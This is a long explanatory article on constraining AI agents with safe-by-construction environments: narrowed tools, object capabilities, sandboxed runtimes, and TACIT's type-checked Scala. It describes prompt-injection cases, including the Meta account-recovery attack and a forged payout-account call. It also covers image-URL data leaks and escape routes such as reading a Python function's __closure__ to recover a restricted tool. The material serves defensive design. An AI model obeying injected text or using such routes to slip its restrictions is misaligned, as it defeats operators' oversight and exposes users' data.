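# Constraining AI agents with programming environments that are safe by construction

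## Agents, the code they produce, and what it means to rule out an unsafe action

An AI agent is a language model that pursues a task by calling tools or running code in a loop. The model produces only text. Other software, called the harness, reads that text and carries out the actions it specifies, such as changing files or sending emails. Whoever builds the harness therefore decides the agent's action space, which is the set of actions the environment lets the agent express and carry out.

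Developers can try to keep an agent from doing harm through behavioural alignment, which means training the model not to take harmful actions that are available to it. They can also take a structural approach, which means using the agent's environment to limit what it can do, whatever the model attempts. The structural approach is older than AI agents. Programming language designers have spent decades making particular mistakes impossible to write, and much of what they built (type systems, restricted interpreters, memory-safe languages, machine-checked proofs) applies to code that agents write.

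### From a model's text to an action

The simplest way for an agent to act is a single tool call. *Code Mode*, a post by Varda and Pai for the network company Cloudflare, describes how one works. A model asked about the weather in Austin outputs a special marker that doesn't correspond to any ordinary text, then a short message in JSON (a plain format for structured data) with the tool's name and arguments, then a closing marker. The harness pauses the model, parses the message, runs the tool and feeds the result back as new input, and the model continues. If a task takes fifty lookups and each has to wait for the one before, the agent goes through this round trip fifty times.

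Many agents now write a program instead of calling tools one at a time. Under Anthropic's *Programmatic tool calling*, a feature for its Claude models, the model writes Python in which each tool appears as an ordinary function, and the platform runs the code in a sandboxed container, which has limited access to anything outside it. The program pauses at each tool call, the developer's application supplies the result, and the program resumes. The model receives only the final output. For example, checking 20 employees against their budgets with individual calls takes 20 round trips and puts thousands of expense lines into the model's input. One script can do all 20 lookups and return only the names of the people who overspent.

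Agents can also complete more tasks when they act by writing programs. Wang, Chen and colleagues (2024), in *Executable Code Actions Elicit Better LLM Agents*, had 17 models act through plain text, JSON and Python on 82 tasks, most of which required several tools. The best model, a version of GPT-4, solved 74.4% of the tasks in Python, compared with 53.7% in text and 52.4% in JSON, and took about two fewer turns. The advantage was smaller on single tool calls, where a program can't make use of loops or stored values. Varda and Pai attribute the models' ease with code to training, because models have seen code from millions of real projects but only a small, contrived set of tool calls.

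Those GPT-4-era models are long out of date, and most figures that companies now publish concern cost. In one example from Anthropic, an agent used 2,000 tokens (the word fragments that models read and write) instead of 150,000 by loading tool definitions only as it needed them. The saving depends heavily on the task. On a project-management benchmark with 75 tools, programs cut billed input tokens by roughly 38% without changing accuracy. On a customer-service benchmark with one or two calls per turn, scores also stayed the same, but the cost rose by about 8%. OpenAI distinguishes work that needs judgment from work that mostly moves, filters and combines data, and uses code for the latter.

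OpenAI's *Programmatic Tool Calling* recommends direct calls by default for writes and for anything that needs a person's consent, so that the point of authorization stays clear. A forty-line script that may issue refunds inside a loop is much harder to approve than a single proposed refund, which a person can judge at a glance. This difficulty is a good part of why the environment matters more once agents act through code.

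### Acting code and shipped code

Fu, Wei and colleagues (2026), in *Code as Agent Harness*, observe that earlier surveys treated code as the end product of a language model, whereas agents increasingly reason and act through code. This difference matters for safety. Acting code is code an agent writes and immediately runs to carry out its task, like the budget script. Shipped code is code an agent writes for software that other people run, like a comment form it adds to a company's website.

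Acting code may exist for only a few seconds, and often nobody reads it. The danger is that it does harm while it runs, such as emailing the wrong person or deleting the wrong folder. Shipped code may run for years on machines the agent never touches, where an outsider could later find a flaw in it. A standard example is SQL injection, in which a program pastes a visitor's text into a database query, so a visitor can change what the query does by typing fragments of query language.

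An operator controls the whole environment in which acting code runs. They can remove the network library, forbid half the language or create a small new one, because no human team has to maintain the scripts afterwards. Shipped code has to fit an existing codebase and run without the agent's harness, so it benefits only from properties it keeps outside that harness. One is memory safety, which Rust guarantees by default and which means that a program never reads or writes memory it has no right to use. The two categories overlap slightly. Anthropic describes agents that save a working script as a reusable function for later tasks, and a script that other people's agents keep calling for a year has become shipped code, regardless of its original purpose.

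### Prompt injection

An agent can do damage by mistake, but the threat that shapes most designs is prompt injection, in which instructions are hidden in material an agent reads to make it serve someone other than its user. Willison, the software developer who named it, explains in *CaMeL offers a promising new direction for mitigating prompt injection attacks* (2025) that he chose the term because SQL injection involves the same mistake. Harnesses join the user's trusted request and the untrusted text of an email or web page into one stream of tokens, and no known method reliably makes a model obey only the trusted part.

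The firm Capsule Security found prompt injection flaws in two commercial products, Microsoft's Copilot Studio and Salesforce's Agentforce, that let attackers extract corporate data through public forms, according to the OECD's *Prompt Injection Attacks Lead to Data Leaks in Microsoft and Salesforce* (2026). Both companies issued patches. SC Media reported that OWASP, a community that publishes security guidance, ranked prompt injection first on its 2026 list of risks to language-model applications.

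Training models to resist attacks and filtering attacks out both make attacks harder, but *Design Patterns for Securing LLM Agents against Prompt Injections* (Beurer-Kellner, Buesser and colleagues, 2025) points out that these defenses give no guarantee. Willison writes that "in application security 99% is a failing grade". If a filter stops 99% of attempts and each attempt is independent, an attacker who tries 100 times gets through at least once with probability 1 − 0.99^100, or about 63%. Real attackers also learn from their failures, so their chance of success is probably higher.

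Beurer-Kellner and colleagues therefore argue that once an agent has taken in untrusted input, its design should make it impossible for that input to trigger any consequential action, even if the model is fooled. In announcing its new list, OWASP (2026) similarly recommends assuming that AI will sometimes fail and putting enforceable controls around what it can reach and do.

### A support agent with two different mail tools

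Take an agent that answers customers' emails. In one design the harness gives it `send(address, text)`. In the other it gives the agent `reply(text)`, which the harness has already bound to the customer who wrote in:

```python
def make_reply(send, customer):
    def reply(text):
        send(customer.address, text)
    return reply
```

The harness calls `make_reply` when a message arrives and passes only the resulting `reply` to the agent. Let A be the set of all email addresses, T the set of all texts and c the customer's address. With `send`, the agent can perform any action in A × T, but with `reply` it can perform only those in {c} × T. This rules out every pair whose address is not c, without inspecting any messages. Even if a hidden instruction leads the model to try to forward the conversation to an attacker's address, the agent has no way to express that action.

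Everything in T remains possible. The agent can send the right customer a rude reply, a false one, or one that repeats an internal note about them. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues make the same point about an assistant that emails a day's schedule to a fixed recipient. Text planted in the calendar can change the body of the email but not who receives it.

Two of the remaining risks are more serious than they look. First, the customer may be the attacker. If the agent can look up anyone's orders, a customer can ask for a stranger's address and `reply` will send it. The lookup tool therefore needs to be restricted like the mail tool, with access only to this customer's records. Second, messages can carry information to third parties. Beurer-Kellner and colleagues mention images that trigger a web request when displayed. An image link with private data in its URL would send that data to whoever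 runs the image server. A `reply` that accepts only plain text prevents this, although a customer could still click on a malicious link.

Giving an agent too broad a tool is a common mistake that OWASP calls excessive agency. *LLM06:2025 Excessive Agency* defines this as the weakness that lets a model's unexpected or manipulated output lead to damaging actions, whatever caused the malfunction. In OWASP's example, an assistant only has to summarize incoming mail but uses a plug-in that can also send it. The suggested remedies include a plug-in that can only read mail and a login with read-only permission.

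Meta ran into a version of this problem in spring 2026 with an AI support assistant that helped locked-out Instagram users recover their accounts. Attackers asked the assistant to link a victim's account to their own email address, and it sent that address a one-time code for resetting the password, Krebs on Security (2026) reported. Because of a bug in a separate code path, the system never checked whether the address belonged to the account, according to The Decoder. The breach began on 17 April and came to light on 31 May, according to Gizmodo, and affected at least 20,225 accounts. Meta disabled the chatbot and removed the code path, This Week in Security reported.

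A recovery tool with no address parameter, which could send codes only to addresses already on file, would have stopped this attack however gullible the assistant was. But narrow tools can also block legitimate uses. This one would have turned away honest users who had lost access to their old address, and helping them was probably one of the reasons for building the assistant.

### Which class, and what must one trust?

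Security engineers group security flaws with the same cause into vulnerability classes, such as SQL injection and buffer overflow (writing past the end of the memory reserved for some data). An environment is safe by construction when any program it accepts is free of a stated class of flaw or unsafe action. The guarantee covers only the stated class. For example, `reply` is safe by construction against email to strangers, but an agent can still use it to send a rude message.

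Often a checker decides which programs to accept. The checker is sound if it accepts no program that breaks its stated guarantee. By Rice's theorem, no algorithm can correctly decide, for every program, whether it has a given non-trivial property of behaviour, so a sound checker for such a property that always finishes will also reject some harmless programs. Partly for that reason, languages offer escape hatches, such as Rust's `unsafe` blocks, which switch off some safety checks. Careful programmers may need these features, but an agent under an attacker's influence can use them to escape its restrictions.

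Python has many such loopholes. Any Python code that holds the `reply` function above can read its `__closure__` attribute and pull out the original `send`. If the machine has network access, agent code could also import Python's standard mail library and bypass `reply` altogether. So the guarantee for `reply` holds only in an environment that blocks both routes.

A guarantee's trusted base is the compiler, runtime and library code that must be correct for the guarantee to hold. For `reply`, this includes the interpreter, the lines of code that bind the address, and the ticketing system that determines who the customer is. If an impostor can open a ticket in someone else's name, `reply` sends its message to the impostor.

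Every mechanism therefore faces two questions: which class does it exclude, and what must one trust for that to hold?

### Four places to enforce a rule

The earliest point at which the harness can rule out an unsafe action is while the model generates text. The model writes one token at a time, and the harness can block any token that would break a given grammar. For a direct tool call, the grammar could allow only one value in the address field. The trusted base is then the grammar and the code that applies it. This method is weaker when the model writes a program, because the text may contain only a variable called `address`, whose value does not exist until the program runs. Anthropic's platform has a strict setting that holds a tool call's arguments to a declared format, but does not support it with programmatic calling.

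A compile-time checker examines the finished program before any of it runs. If `send` is out of scope, a program that mentions it produces an error and no email is sent. In *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* (Odersky, Zhao and colleagues, 2026), agents write Scala under a type checker that tracks capabilities, which are unforgeable references that both name a resource and grant the right to use it. The paper stresses that the resulting guarantee covers all inputs, not just the tested ones. Relying on that guarantee requires trusting the checker's soundness, the compiler and any library the program calls. The checker cannot use facts that are available only when the program runs, such as whether an address the program finds in an email belongs to a colleague or an attacker.

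An interpreter or library can use those facts while the program runs. Willison describes CaMeL, a Google DeepMind system in which an interpreter for a restricted form of Python tracks the sources of each value. It can allow an email if the recipient is trusted and ask the user otherwise. The interpreter and the policy both become part of the trusted base, and somebody has to write the policy. The interpreter can also refuse an action after earlier steps have already changed something.

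The operating system is the outermost of the four. It can confine a process to certain files and network connections whatever language the program uses, but this requires trusting the system's own isolation code. It can restrict the support agent to the company's mail server, but its rules are too coarse to separate a message to the customer from one to a stranger, because both travel over the same connection. Varda and Pai dislike network filters for a related reason: the supervisor struggles to tell which traffic a task needs, and the model has to guess what the filter will block.

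Cloudflare's alternative combines a run-time rule with isolation, and it also fixes the hole in `reply`. Cloudflare runs the agent's program in a sandbox without internet access and gives it live objects that stand for particular services. When the program calls one of these objects, the call goes to a supervisor outside the sandbox, which holds the access keys and makes the real request. If `reply` were built this way, inspecting the object would reveal only a channel to the supervisor, because `send` and the customer's address would be outside the sandbox.

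## Object capabilities: giving code only the authority it needs

The live objects that Cloudflare gives to an agent's program follow a design from the 1960s. In the object-capability model, a program can affect the outside world only through capabilities, which name a resource and grant the right to use it. The program has only the capabilities it was given or made from what it already had.

Most software runs on ambient authority, which is permission a program has merely by running. A Python script run on a laptop can usually read or delete any file its user can, even if its task doesn't involve files. *Capability Myths Demolished* (Miller, Yee and Shapiro, 2003) compares this to a world with doors but no keys, where each door opens by itself for the right person. Because the program never has to present a key, it doesn't specify which of its permissions to use.

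Jack Dennis and Earl Van Horn of MIT described the alternative in 1966, for computers that many people shared. Their system kept a list of capabilities for each computation. Each entry pointed to an object, such as a segment of memory, and recorded what the computation could do with it, for example read it but not change it. A program referred to an object by its entry's position in the list. Position 3 in one list had no connection with position 3 in another, so a program could not reach someone else's data by guessing numbers.

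An agent's tool calls work in much the same way. The model outputs the name of a tool, and the harness looks it up in the list of tools for that session. If the model follows an instruction in a malicious email to call `delete_database` and the list has no such tool, the call fails. The arguments are less safe because an account number or a file path is only text. It identifies a thing without granting any right to it, so the tool has to use its own permissions to act on it. Norm Hardy, who worked on operating systems, encountered this problem long before AI agents existed.

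### The confused deputy

In *The Confused Deputy* (1988), Hardy tells a nearly true story about Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Tymshare kept a compiler in a directory called SYSX. Anyone who ran the compiler could name a file for its debugging output. The staff also had the compiler collect statistics on how people used the language and write them to a file called STAT in SYSX. To allow this, they gave the compiler permission to write to any file in SYSX.

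The company's billing records were also in SYSX, in a file called BILL. A user who had learned that name gave it to the compiler as the file for debugging output. When the compiler tried to open BILL for writing, the operating system checked the compiler's license, which covered SYSX, and opened the file. The debugging output overwrote the billing records.

The user had no permission to change BILL, but the compiler did. Hardy calls the compiler a confused deputy because it had authority from both Tymshare and the user and no way to keep the two apart. It was supposed to use Tymshare's authority for the statistics and the user's for the debugging output, but it could not specify which to use when it opened a file.

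The obvious repairs don't work well. The compiler could refuse to write debugging output to other directories, but users often had good reason to ask for that. It could refuse file names in SYSX, but some people had legitimate access to SYSX. It could refuse the name BILL, but the directory held other sensitive files, and somebody would have to update the compiler whenever a new one appeared. Tymshare eventually added a system call that let a program choose which of its two authorities to use, but some programs soon needed more than two. The last time Hardy wrote down the rules for opening a file, they contained fourteen "and"s and "or"s.

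With capabilities, the caller passes an open file instead of a name:

```python
# The compiler opens the file with whatever permission it has.
compile(program, "(SYSX)BILL")

# The caller passes a file that it can already write to.
compile(program, debug_file)
```

In the second version, the compiler holds its own capability for STAT and uses it only for statistics. It writes debugging output using the capability the user passes to it. A user who can't write to BILL has no capability for that file to pass, so the attack fails without any check on file names. Hardy had worried that the capabilities would fill the machine's storage. In practice, they replaced so many other mechanisms that his capability systems were usually smaller than equivalent conventional ones.

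Hardy's advice, as the blog Habitat Chronicles (2017) reports it, was "don't separate designation from authority". Unix users can see the difference in two ways of copying a file. The command `cp a b` receives two names and opens the files itself, so it needs permission to open anything the user might name. With `cat < a > b`, the user's shell opens both files and passes them to `cat`, which could in principle do its job with no other access at all. (Unix gives `cat` the user's full permissions anyway.)

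Miller and colleagues dispute the common view that access control lists and capabilities differ only in bookkeeping. Both can be shown as a table of which users or programs have which rights to which files. Conventional systems store the table by column, as an access control list for each file, and capability systems store it by row, as a list for each program. Miller and colleagues object that the table omits how rights change and how programs refer to files. In an access control list, the file's entry points to the user, so the program still needs a separate name for the file, and Hardy's problem returns. The lists also tend to identify people, because people change less often than running programs do. An agent that runs under an employee's account therefore gets all of the employee's permissions, for a task that may need only one folder.

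### Prompt injection and the deputy

An agent that reads a stranger's email while it holds the company's payment key looks a lot like Tymshare's compiler. Suresh and Gao (2026) make this connection in *AGENTCAP* and point out that an injected instruction doesn't need to get past an authorization check, because it can redirect an agent that is already authorized.

Mellafe Zuvic (2026), in *Capability Gates Are Not Authorization*, looked for this flaw in the public code of three toolkits for building agents: LangChain/LangGraph, LlamaIndex and the Stripe Agent Toolkit. All three let a developer choose which tools an agent sees (the "capability gate" of the title), but none checks by default whether a call is allowed to use the values the model supplied. One demonstration used a fixed model output containing a call to change a simulated merchant's payout account to `acct_ATTACKER_999`. LangChain's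 default code made the change because the account number was a well-formed string. A check against a list of approved accounts blocked the same call.

Mellafe Zuvic wrote the malicious output by hand, so the demonstration doesn't show how often models produce such output. In a companion test of 27 models, when an injected request looked like a necessary part of the user's task, the 12 cheaper models attempted the unauthorized action about 60% of the time on average, and the 15 flagship models about 19%. These attempts took place in a sandbox, so the rates are weak evidence of how often real attacks succeed.

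Sources differ on what counts as a confused deputy. *A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (2026) uses the term only when the agent has a permission that its own user lacks. In its example, an employee asks an agent for everyone's salaries, and the agent fetches them from a personnel database that the employee can't open. Running the agent with the employee's permissions would prevent this, but it would not help when a malicious email turns an agent against the employee, because the employee can read the files the attacker wants. A stricter rule, from an online discussion between Willison and Baibhav Bista, is that while a model processes information from some party, its privileges should drop to those of that party. An agent reading a stranger's email could then do only what the operator would let the stranger do.

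The comparison with Hardy's compiler is also limited, because a language model decides which capability to use by reading text, and an attacker may have written some of that text. The compiler had separate pieces of code for statistics and debugging output, so once each piece had its own capability, nothing a user typed could swap them. *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, a 2025 article by David C for the UK's National Cyber Security Centre, argues that developers can fix an ordinary confused deputy, but that a language model is an "inherently confusable deputy". If an agent can read a private folder and post to a public forum, an injected instruction can get it to read the folder and post the contents, even though it holds each capability for a good reason.

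Capabilities limit what a fooled agent can do, but they don't stop it from being fooled. David C therefore advises designers to consider the worst an attacker could do with direct access to the agent's tools. The harness can reduce the possible harm by choosing the target itself before the model reads anything untrusted, as it does when it binds `reply` to one customer.

### How a program comes to hold a capability

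To work out the worst case, a designer needs to know every way a program can gain access to something. *Robust Composition* (Miller, 2006), a doctoral thesis built around a secure language called E, shows that there are only four. Miller illustrates them with three objects in a running program, Alice, Bob and Carol, by showing how Bob can get a reference to Carol.

Bob may have had a reference to Carol in the initial conditions. Bob may have created Carol, in which case he has the only reference to her until he shares it. Alice may have created Bob and given him a reference to Carol that she already had. Alice may also introduce them, if she has references to both, by sending Bob a message that contains her reference to Carol.

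The support agent from the previous section uses several of these. The harness has `send` from the start. It creates `reply` and endows it with `send` and the customer's address. Then it introduces `reply` to the agent's program by passing it in. The program can't get `send` unless an object that has it passes it to the program, and `reply` never does.

So if no chain of references connects two groups of objects, they can never become connected, because no object has references to both groups and could give one a reference to the other. An operator can therefore find an upper limit on what a program can reach by tracing the graph of references.

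Miller distinguishes permission, which is a direct reference to an object, from authority, which is the ability to affect the object by any open route, including through others. If Bob can talk to Alice, Alice can write to the password file, and Alice writes whatever Bob asks, then Bob has authority over the password file without having permission to access it. Similarly, an agent whose only tool is a chat channel to a coding agent may be able to run any command that the coding agent will run on request. Communication between agents often implies authority in Miller's sense, although Suresh and Gao write that it doesn't, on the grounds that their system checks the second agent's own capabilities when it acts.

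Let EA be the set of effects that a program will eventually be able to cause. Nobody can compute EA in practice, because it depends on how all the other programs behave. Miller uses two larger sets. TA is what the program could cause if every object it can reach misused everything it holds. BA is smaller, because it takes into account the known behavior of some trusted objects. Then

EA ⊆ BA ⊆ TA,

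and an effect that is missing from BA or TA can't happen. For the support agent, TA includes email to anyone, because `reply` holds `send`. BA includes only email to the customer, because anyone who reads the code of `reply` can see that it always uses the customer's address. This suggests a sensible way to divide the work. The operator assumes the worst about the code the model writes, and carefully checks the few lines of wrapper code that stand between it and the outside world.

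These limits apply only to channels that the system explicitly provides. Miller leaves out covert channels, such as when one program signals another by varying how long it keeps the processor busy.

### What the language has to forbid

The four rules hold only if the language gives programs no other way to obtain references. In particular, a program must not be able to forge them. C++ allows forgery because a program can turn any integer into a memory address and use whatever is stored there. Object capabilities therefore require memory safety.

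Second, an object's private contents must stay private. Python fails this requirement because any code can read a function's `__closure__`, as the previous section described. Some reflection (a program's ability to inspect or call parts of itself) is harmless. For example, E has a function that sends any message to any object the caller already holds, which lets the caller do nothing it couldn't already do.

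Third, programs must not have ambient input and output. A Python program can call `open` or import a network library even if no one passed it a file or a connection. Miller calls these "magic names" because the language connects them to real authority that whoever loaded the program never supplied and can't withhold.

Fourth, components must not share global variables that they can change. Otherwise, two components with no references to each other could still pass capabilities to each other through such a variable.

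E meets these conditions by design. Its loader takes a piece of code and a table of values for the names that the code uses but doesn't define. A few built-in names such as `true` and `throw` work without an entry, but they carry no authority. Whoever loads the code can deny it access to the network by leaving the network out of the table.

Joe-E supports object capabilities by restricting Java. Java is already memory-safe, but its global (static) variables can change, and a loader can't withhold certain system classes that carry authority. Joe-E requires every static variable to be constant and to contain only data that can never change, and it limits which parts of Java's library a program may call.

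Hardened JavaScript, a more recent project, starts from a language with no built-in file or network functions, which browsers and servers add as global variables. Its `lockdown` function freezes the built-in objects that all JavaScript code shares, such as the one that defines how arrays behave, so that one component can't tamper with them to attack another. The host then runs untrusted code in a `Compartment`, which has only the standard harmless global variables and any the host adds. The Scala subset that Odersky and colleagues use for agents bans unchecked type casts and run-time reflection for similar reasons, and also tracks capabilities in types.

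### Narrowing access and taking it back

A capability often grants more than a task needs. Instead of adding a permission system, a programmer can write a small object that holds the powerful capability and passes on only some requests. This is attenuation. Here is a read-only view of a folder:

```python
def read_only(folder):
    def list_files():
        return folder.list_files()
    def read(name):
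        return folder.open(name).read()
    return list_files, read
```

An agent that receives these two functions can look through the folder but can't change it. Such wrappers are short but easy to get wrong. If `read` returned the open file instead of its text, the agent could call the file's `write` method. The folder's `open` method must also reject names that lead outside the folder.

Critics of capabilities have long claimed that nobody can take one back after handing it out. That is literally true, but David Redell showed in 1974 how to get the same result with a forwarder that its maker can switch off:

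```python
def make_revocable(target):
    enabled = True
    def forward(*args):
        if not enabled:
            raise PermissionError
        return target(*args)
    def switch_off():
        nonlocal enabled
        enabled = False
    return forward, switch_off
```

The harness gives `forward` to the agent and keeps `switch_off` for itself. When the task ends, it calls `switch_off`, and `forward` becomes useless. If the agent has passed `forward` to a second agent in the meantime, that agent loses access too, because it never had anything except the forwarder. (In ordinary Python both examples still have the `__closure__` problem, so they need a language or a boundary that protects what functions contain.)

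Switching off a forwarder does not revoke other capabilities that the target has already returned through it. Miller's solution is a membrane, which puts a forwarder around every capability that passes through in either direction and switches them all off together. No forwarder can take back information that an agent has already read, such as a customer list.

Forwarders also make audits harder. A list of everyone with direct access to a file includes the forwarder's owner, but not the people who reach the file through the forwarder. Handing out only restricted access is good practice, but it makes that list less informative.

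Suresh and Gao apply both ideas to agents that call tools. In their system, an agent that wants to call a tool first states what the call is for. A policy engine outside the model then decides whether to issue a signed capability for that action. In their sample policy for a bank, a capability to send money lasts 30 seconds and covers one call. An agent can delegate to another agent only by narrowing. If the original allows action *a* on resource *r*, with *b* calls, expiry time *e* and *d* further delegations, the delegated one must satisfy

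a′ = a, r′ = r, b′ ≤ b, e′ ≤ e, d′ < d.

Since *d* falls at every step, delegation chains have a maximum length. The system also withdraws access from agents that behave suspiciously. Each agent starts with a trust score of 0.8, and each refused or anomalous call multiplies it by 0.7. After two such calls the score is 0.392 and the agent can no longer write anything. After three it is 0.274, and the system revokes all the agent's access.

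Suresh and Gao tested this on 949 attacks from AgentDojo, a benchmark of office, banking and travel tasks with planted instructions, and 1,054 from InjecAgent, a similar benchmark. With GPT-5.4, no attack succeeded, and the system lowered the share of users' tasks that agents completed under attack by at most 4.18 percentage points. These results are good, but they come from single runs, and the researchers wrote the policies for each benchmark after seeing its tools. A company would have to write its own policies, and Suresh and Gao acknowledge that the system can't compensate for a policy that allows too much.

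A related design goes further by making every permission single-use. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Context-to-Execution Integrity for LLM Agents*, addresses what he calls authority laundering, in which text that should serve only as evidence gains the power to trigger an action. For example, an agent may use an error log to find out which file is broken, but text in the log should not be able to start a command on the company's live database. His system issues a capability for one exact action and uses it up just before the action runs, so injected text can't get the agent to repeat the action or use the permission for something else. In 400 trials on code repositories, no unauthorized action got through, and agents completed 231 of the tasks safely.

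### Runtimes that start with nothing

Those two systems check individual tool calls. When an agent writes programs, the runtime that executes them has to enforce the limits. By 2026, developers had several runtimes that start a program with almost no authority.

WebAssembly is a compact instruction format that browsers and servers can run in isolation. A WebAssembly program starts with its own block of memory and can perform any computation, but the format has no instruction for opening a file or contacting a server, so the program has to call functions that the host supplies. WASI, the WebAssembly System Interface, is a standard set of these functions. To grant access to a folder, the host opens it in advance and gives the program a handle to it. The program can then open files only by paths relative to that folder.

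The operator still has to trust the engine that translates WebAssembly into machine code and the host's functions, including the code that stops a path from leading out of the folder. The boundary also surrounds the program as a whole. To run Python this way, developers usually compile the entire interpreter to WebAssembly, so every line of the agent's script shares whatever access the interpreter was given. Python's `__closure__` still works inside the boundary, so `send` has to stay on the host's side.

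Cloudflare's code mode uses isolates, which are separate instances of V8, the JavaScript engine in Google Chrome. The agent's code starts with no file system, no environment variables (settings in which developers often store passwords) and, by default, no internet access, according to Cloudflare's *Code Mode: give agents an entire API in 1,000 tokens*. The host gives the code authority by passing in named objects. In an example from Varda, Pai and Gupta's *Sandboxing AI agents, 100x faster*, the host passes in an object called `CHAT_ROOM`, whose three methods read the chat history, subscribe to new messages and post a message. If the agent only has to summarize the chat, the host could leave out the method for posting.

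Isolates also start quickly enough to be used once and discarded. According to Varda and colleagues, an isolate starts in a few milliseconds, while a container (the more common way to package and isolate a program) takes hundreds. When startup is slow, operators may be tempted to reuse a container for several tasks, which is a security risk because one task can leave something behind for the next.

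How well code mode constrains an agent still depends on how much authority the host gives each function. In one of Cloudflare's examples, the agent's code gets a function called `request`, which takes the path of any operation in Cloudflare's interface. The access key stays outside the sandbox, so the code can't steal it, but while the code runs, it can use the key to do anything the key allows. An injected instruction could influence the path, which is plain text. Hiding the key is worthwhile, but to limit what the code can do with it, the operator needs a key with fewer rights or a wrapper with fewer functions.

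The trusted base for isolates is large. Varda and colleagues acknowledge that security bugs are more common in V8 than in typical hypervisors, the software that separates virtual machines. Cloudflare installs V8's security fixes within hours and adds a second sandbox around the first. Anyone running isolates on their own servers would have to do similar work.

Small, purpose-built interpreters are a third option. Monty, which the software company Pydantic released in early 2026, runs a subset of Python and is written in Rust. A script in Monty starts with the basic language and a few harmless library modules. It has no direct access to files, the network or environment variables, and can reach the outside world only by calling functions the developer supplies. The developer has to trust those functions and the interpreter, which is far smaller than V8 or the standard Python interpreter. Scripts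 can't use most of Python's libraries, but this is less of a problem for an agent than for a human team, because the scripts are short and the model can usually rewrite one that fails.

Other sandboxes start with a complete language and remove the dangerous parts, and their record is poor. Python once had a restricted mode of this kind, but its developers disabled it in 2003 because it had security holes they couldn't readily fix. About ten years later, the developer of pysandbox, a replacement, gave up on it and called it broken by design. The maintainers of vm2, a popular sandbox for server-side JavaScript, discontinued it in 2023 after a series of critical flaws.

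These projects had a harder task than the designers of E or Monty. Python and JavaScript give programs many ways to get from one object to another, so anyone who builds a sandbox by removing features has to find and block every route that leads to real authority, and do so again whenever a new version of the language adds a feature. An interpreter that starts with nothing has no feature like `__closure__` unless somebody writes it. Such an interpreter can still have bugs, as V8 does, but an attacker has to find one, whereas a sandbox built by removal can fail even when every feature of the language works as designed.

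## Tracking an agent's capabilities in the type system

A runtime that grants no capabilities by default limits which capabilities an agent's program holds, but not how the program combines them. An agent that legitimately needs to read private contracts and post to a website can still post the contracts. To prevent that, the environment has to establish that the piece of code that handles the contracts cannot send anything out.

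A type system can establish this before the program runs. TACIT (Tracked Agent Capabilities In Types), which Odersky and colleagues built at EPFL, a technical university in Lausanne, has agents write short programs in Scala 3. The Scala compiler checks each program, TACIT runs it only if it passes, and the agent gets back either the output or the compiler's error message. TACIT connects through the Model Context Protocol, a common standard for offering tools to models, so agents such as Claude Code can use it unmodified. According to lampepfl's *TACIT*, the research group's code repository, the operator should switch off the agent's own file, shell and network tools. Otherwise the agent can use them to bypass the checks.

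### What a capture set records

A type usually describes the shape of a value. For example, `String` is the type of text, and `String => Int` is the type of a function that takes text and returns a whole number. Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, adds a capture set to the type, which lists the capabilities that the value may hold.

Suppose `f` is a capability for one file. The function `(s: String) => f.write(s)` has the type `String ->{f} Unit`, because anyone who calls it can write to `f` (`Unit` means that it returns nothing useful). A function that only counts the letters in its input has the type `String -> Int`, with no capture set like `{f}` after the arrow. Such a function is pure, meaning that it holds no capabilities, so it can't write to a file, contact a server or print. In a type, the ordinary arrow `=>` allows a function to hold any capability.

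The compiler infers most capture sets and follows chains of references. If a logger holds `f` and a function uses the logger, the compiler detects that the function can affect `f`. It traces references for each value, just as an operator can trace them for a whole program.

A value with fewer capabilities can go anywhere that allows more. For a type T and capture sets C₁ and C₂,

if C₁ ⊆ C₂, then T^C₁ <: T^C₂,

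where <: means "is a subtype of". A pure function therefore fits everywhere, while a function that holds `f` doesn't fit where the program requires a pure one. Capture sets are upper limits. A function that writes to `f` only on Fridays has `f` in its type all week, and the compiler will reject it as impure even if today is Tuesday.

### Capabilities that end with their block

TACIT's library lends out access for the length of a block of code. To use files, the agent calls `requestFileSystem` with the name of a folder and a block. The library passes the block a capability for that folder and returns whatever the block returns. An agent might try to keep the access for later by returning a function that uses it:

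```scala
val later = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("payroll.csv").read()
}
later()
```

The compiler rejects this program. The inner function's type has to include `fs`, but the type of the block's result can't, because `fs` doesn't exist outside the block. Putting the function in a container or assigning it to an outside variable fails for the same reason. The compiler catches the late call before the program runs, while a revocable forwarder, as in the previous section, would block the call only when it happened.

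The check also catches less obvious cases. Scala's *Capture Checking*, the reference page for the feature, compares two programs that square a list of numbers and log each step to a temporary file. The compiler accepts the version with an ordinary list, because all the writing happens inside the block. It rejects the version with a lazy list, which computes each element only when it is needed, because the file may be closed by then.

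Some checks still happen at run time. The compiler can't determine where every path leads, so the library rejects paths outside the folder. It also checks network access against a list of permitted hosts, and access to other programs against a list of permitted commands.

### Data the agent can process but not read

The operator marks some files as classified. When the agent's program reads one, it gets a `Classified[String]`, a wrapper around the text. The main way to work with the contents is the wrapper's `map` method, which applies a function to the hidden text and wraps the result. `map` accepts only pure functions. The compiler accepts this program:

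```scala
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val report = readClassified("secrets/incident.txt")
  val opening = report.map(text => text.take(500))
  writeClassified("secrets/opening.txt", opening)
}
```

The function inside `map` keeps the first 500 characters and holds no capabilities. Its result stays wrapped, and the program saves it to another classified file. The next program tries to copy the report to a public file, and the compiler rejects it:

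```scala
requestFileSystem("/project") {
  val report = readClassified("secrets/incident.txt")
  val notes = access("public/notes.txt")
  report.map(text => notes.write(text))
}
```

This time the function uses `notes`, so its type is `String ->{notes} Unit`, but `map` requires a function with an empty capture set. The compiler reports to the agent that `notes` can't flow into that empty set. The program can't get around this by opening a new folder inside `map`, because `requestFileSystem` needs a capability that a pure function can't hold.

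Odersky and colleagues call this local purity, meaning that the code that handles the secret can't write files or use the network, even though the program as a whole can. They argue that older capability languages such as E can't guarantee this because those languages enforce their limits only at run time.

Working on a document often requires understanding it, so TACIT provides a `chat` function that sends classified text to a second language model the operator trusts, such as one running on the company's own machines. The function returns the reply wrapped as classified data. The main agent's model, usually a cloud service, never receives the text or the reply.

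TACIT writes a program's printed output to two channels, one for the agent and one for the user's terminal. Ordinary values look the same on both, but for a classified value, the user sees the actual contents and the agent sees only the placeholder `Classified(****)`. Suppose a user asks for a summary of a secret contract and then asks how long the summary is. The agent's second program can measure the summary with `map` and print the result. The user sees both the summary and its length, while the agent sees the placeholder each time. The first program's folder access has expired by then, but the second program can still use the wrapped summary because it is only data.

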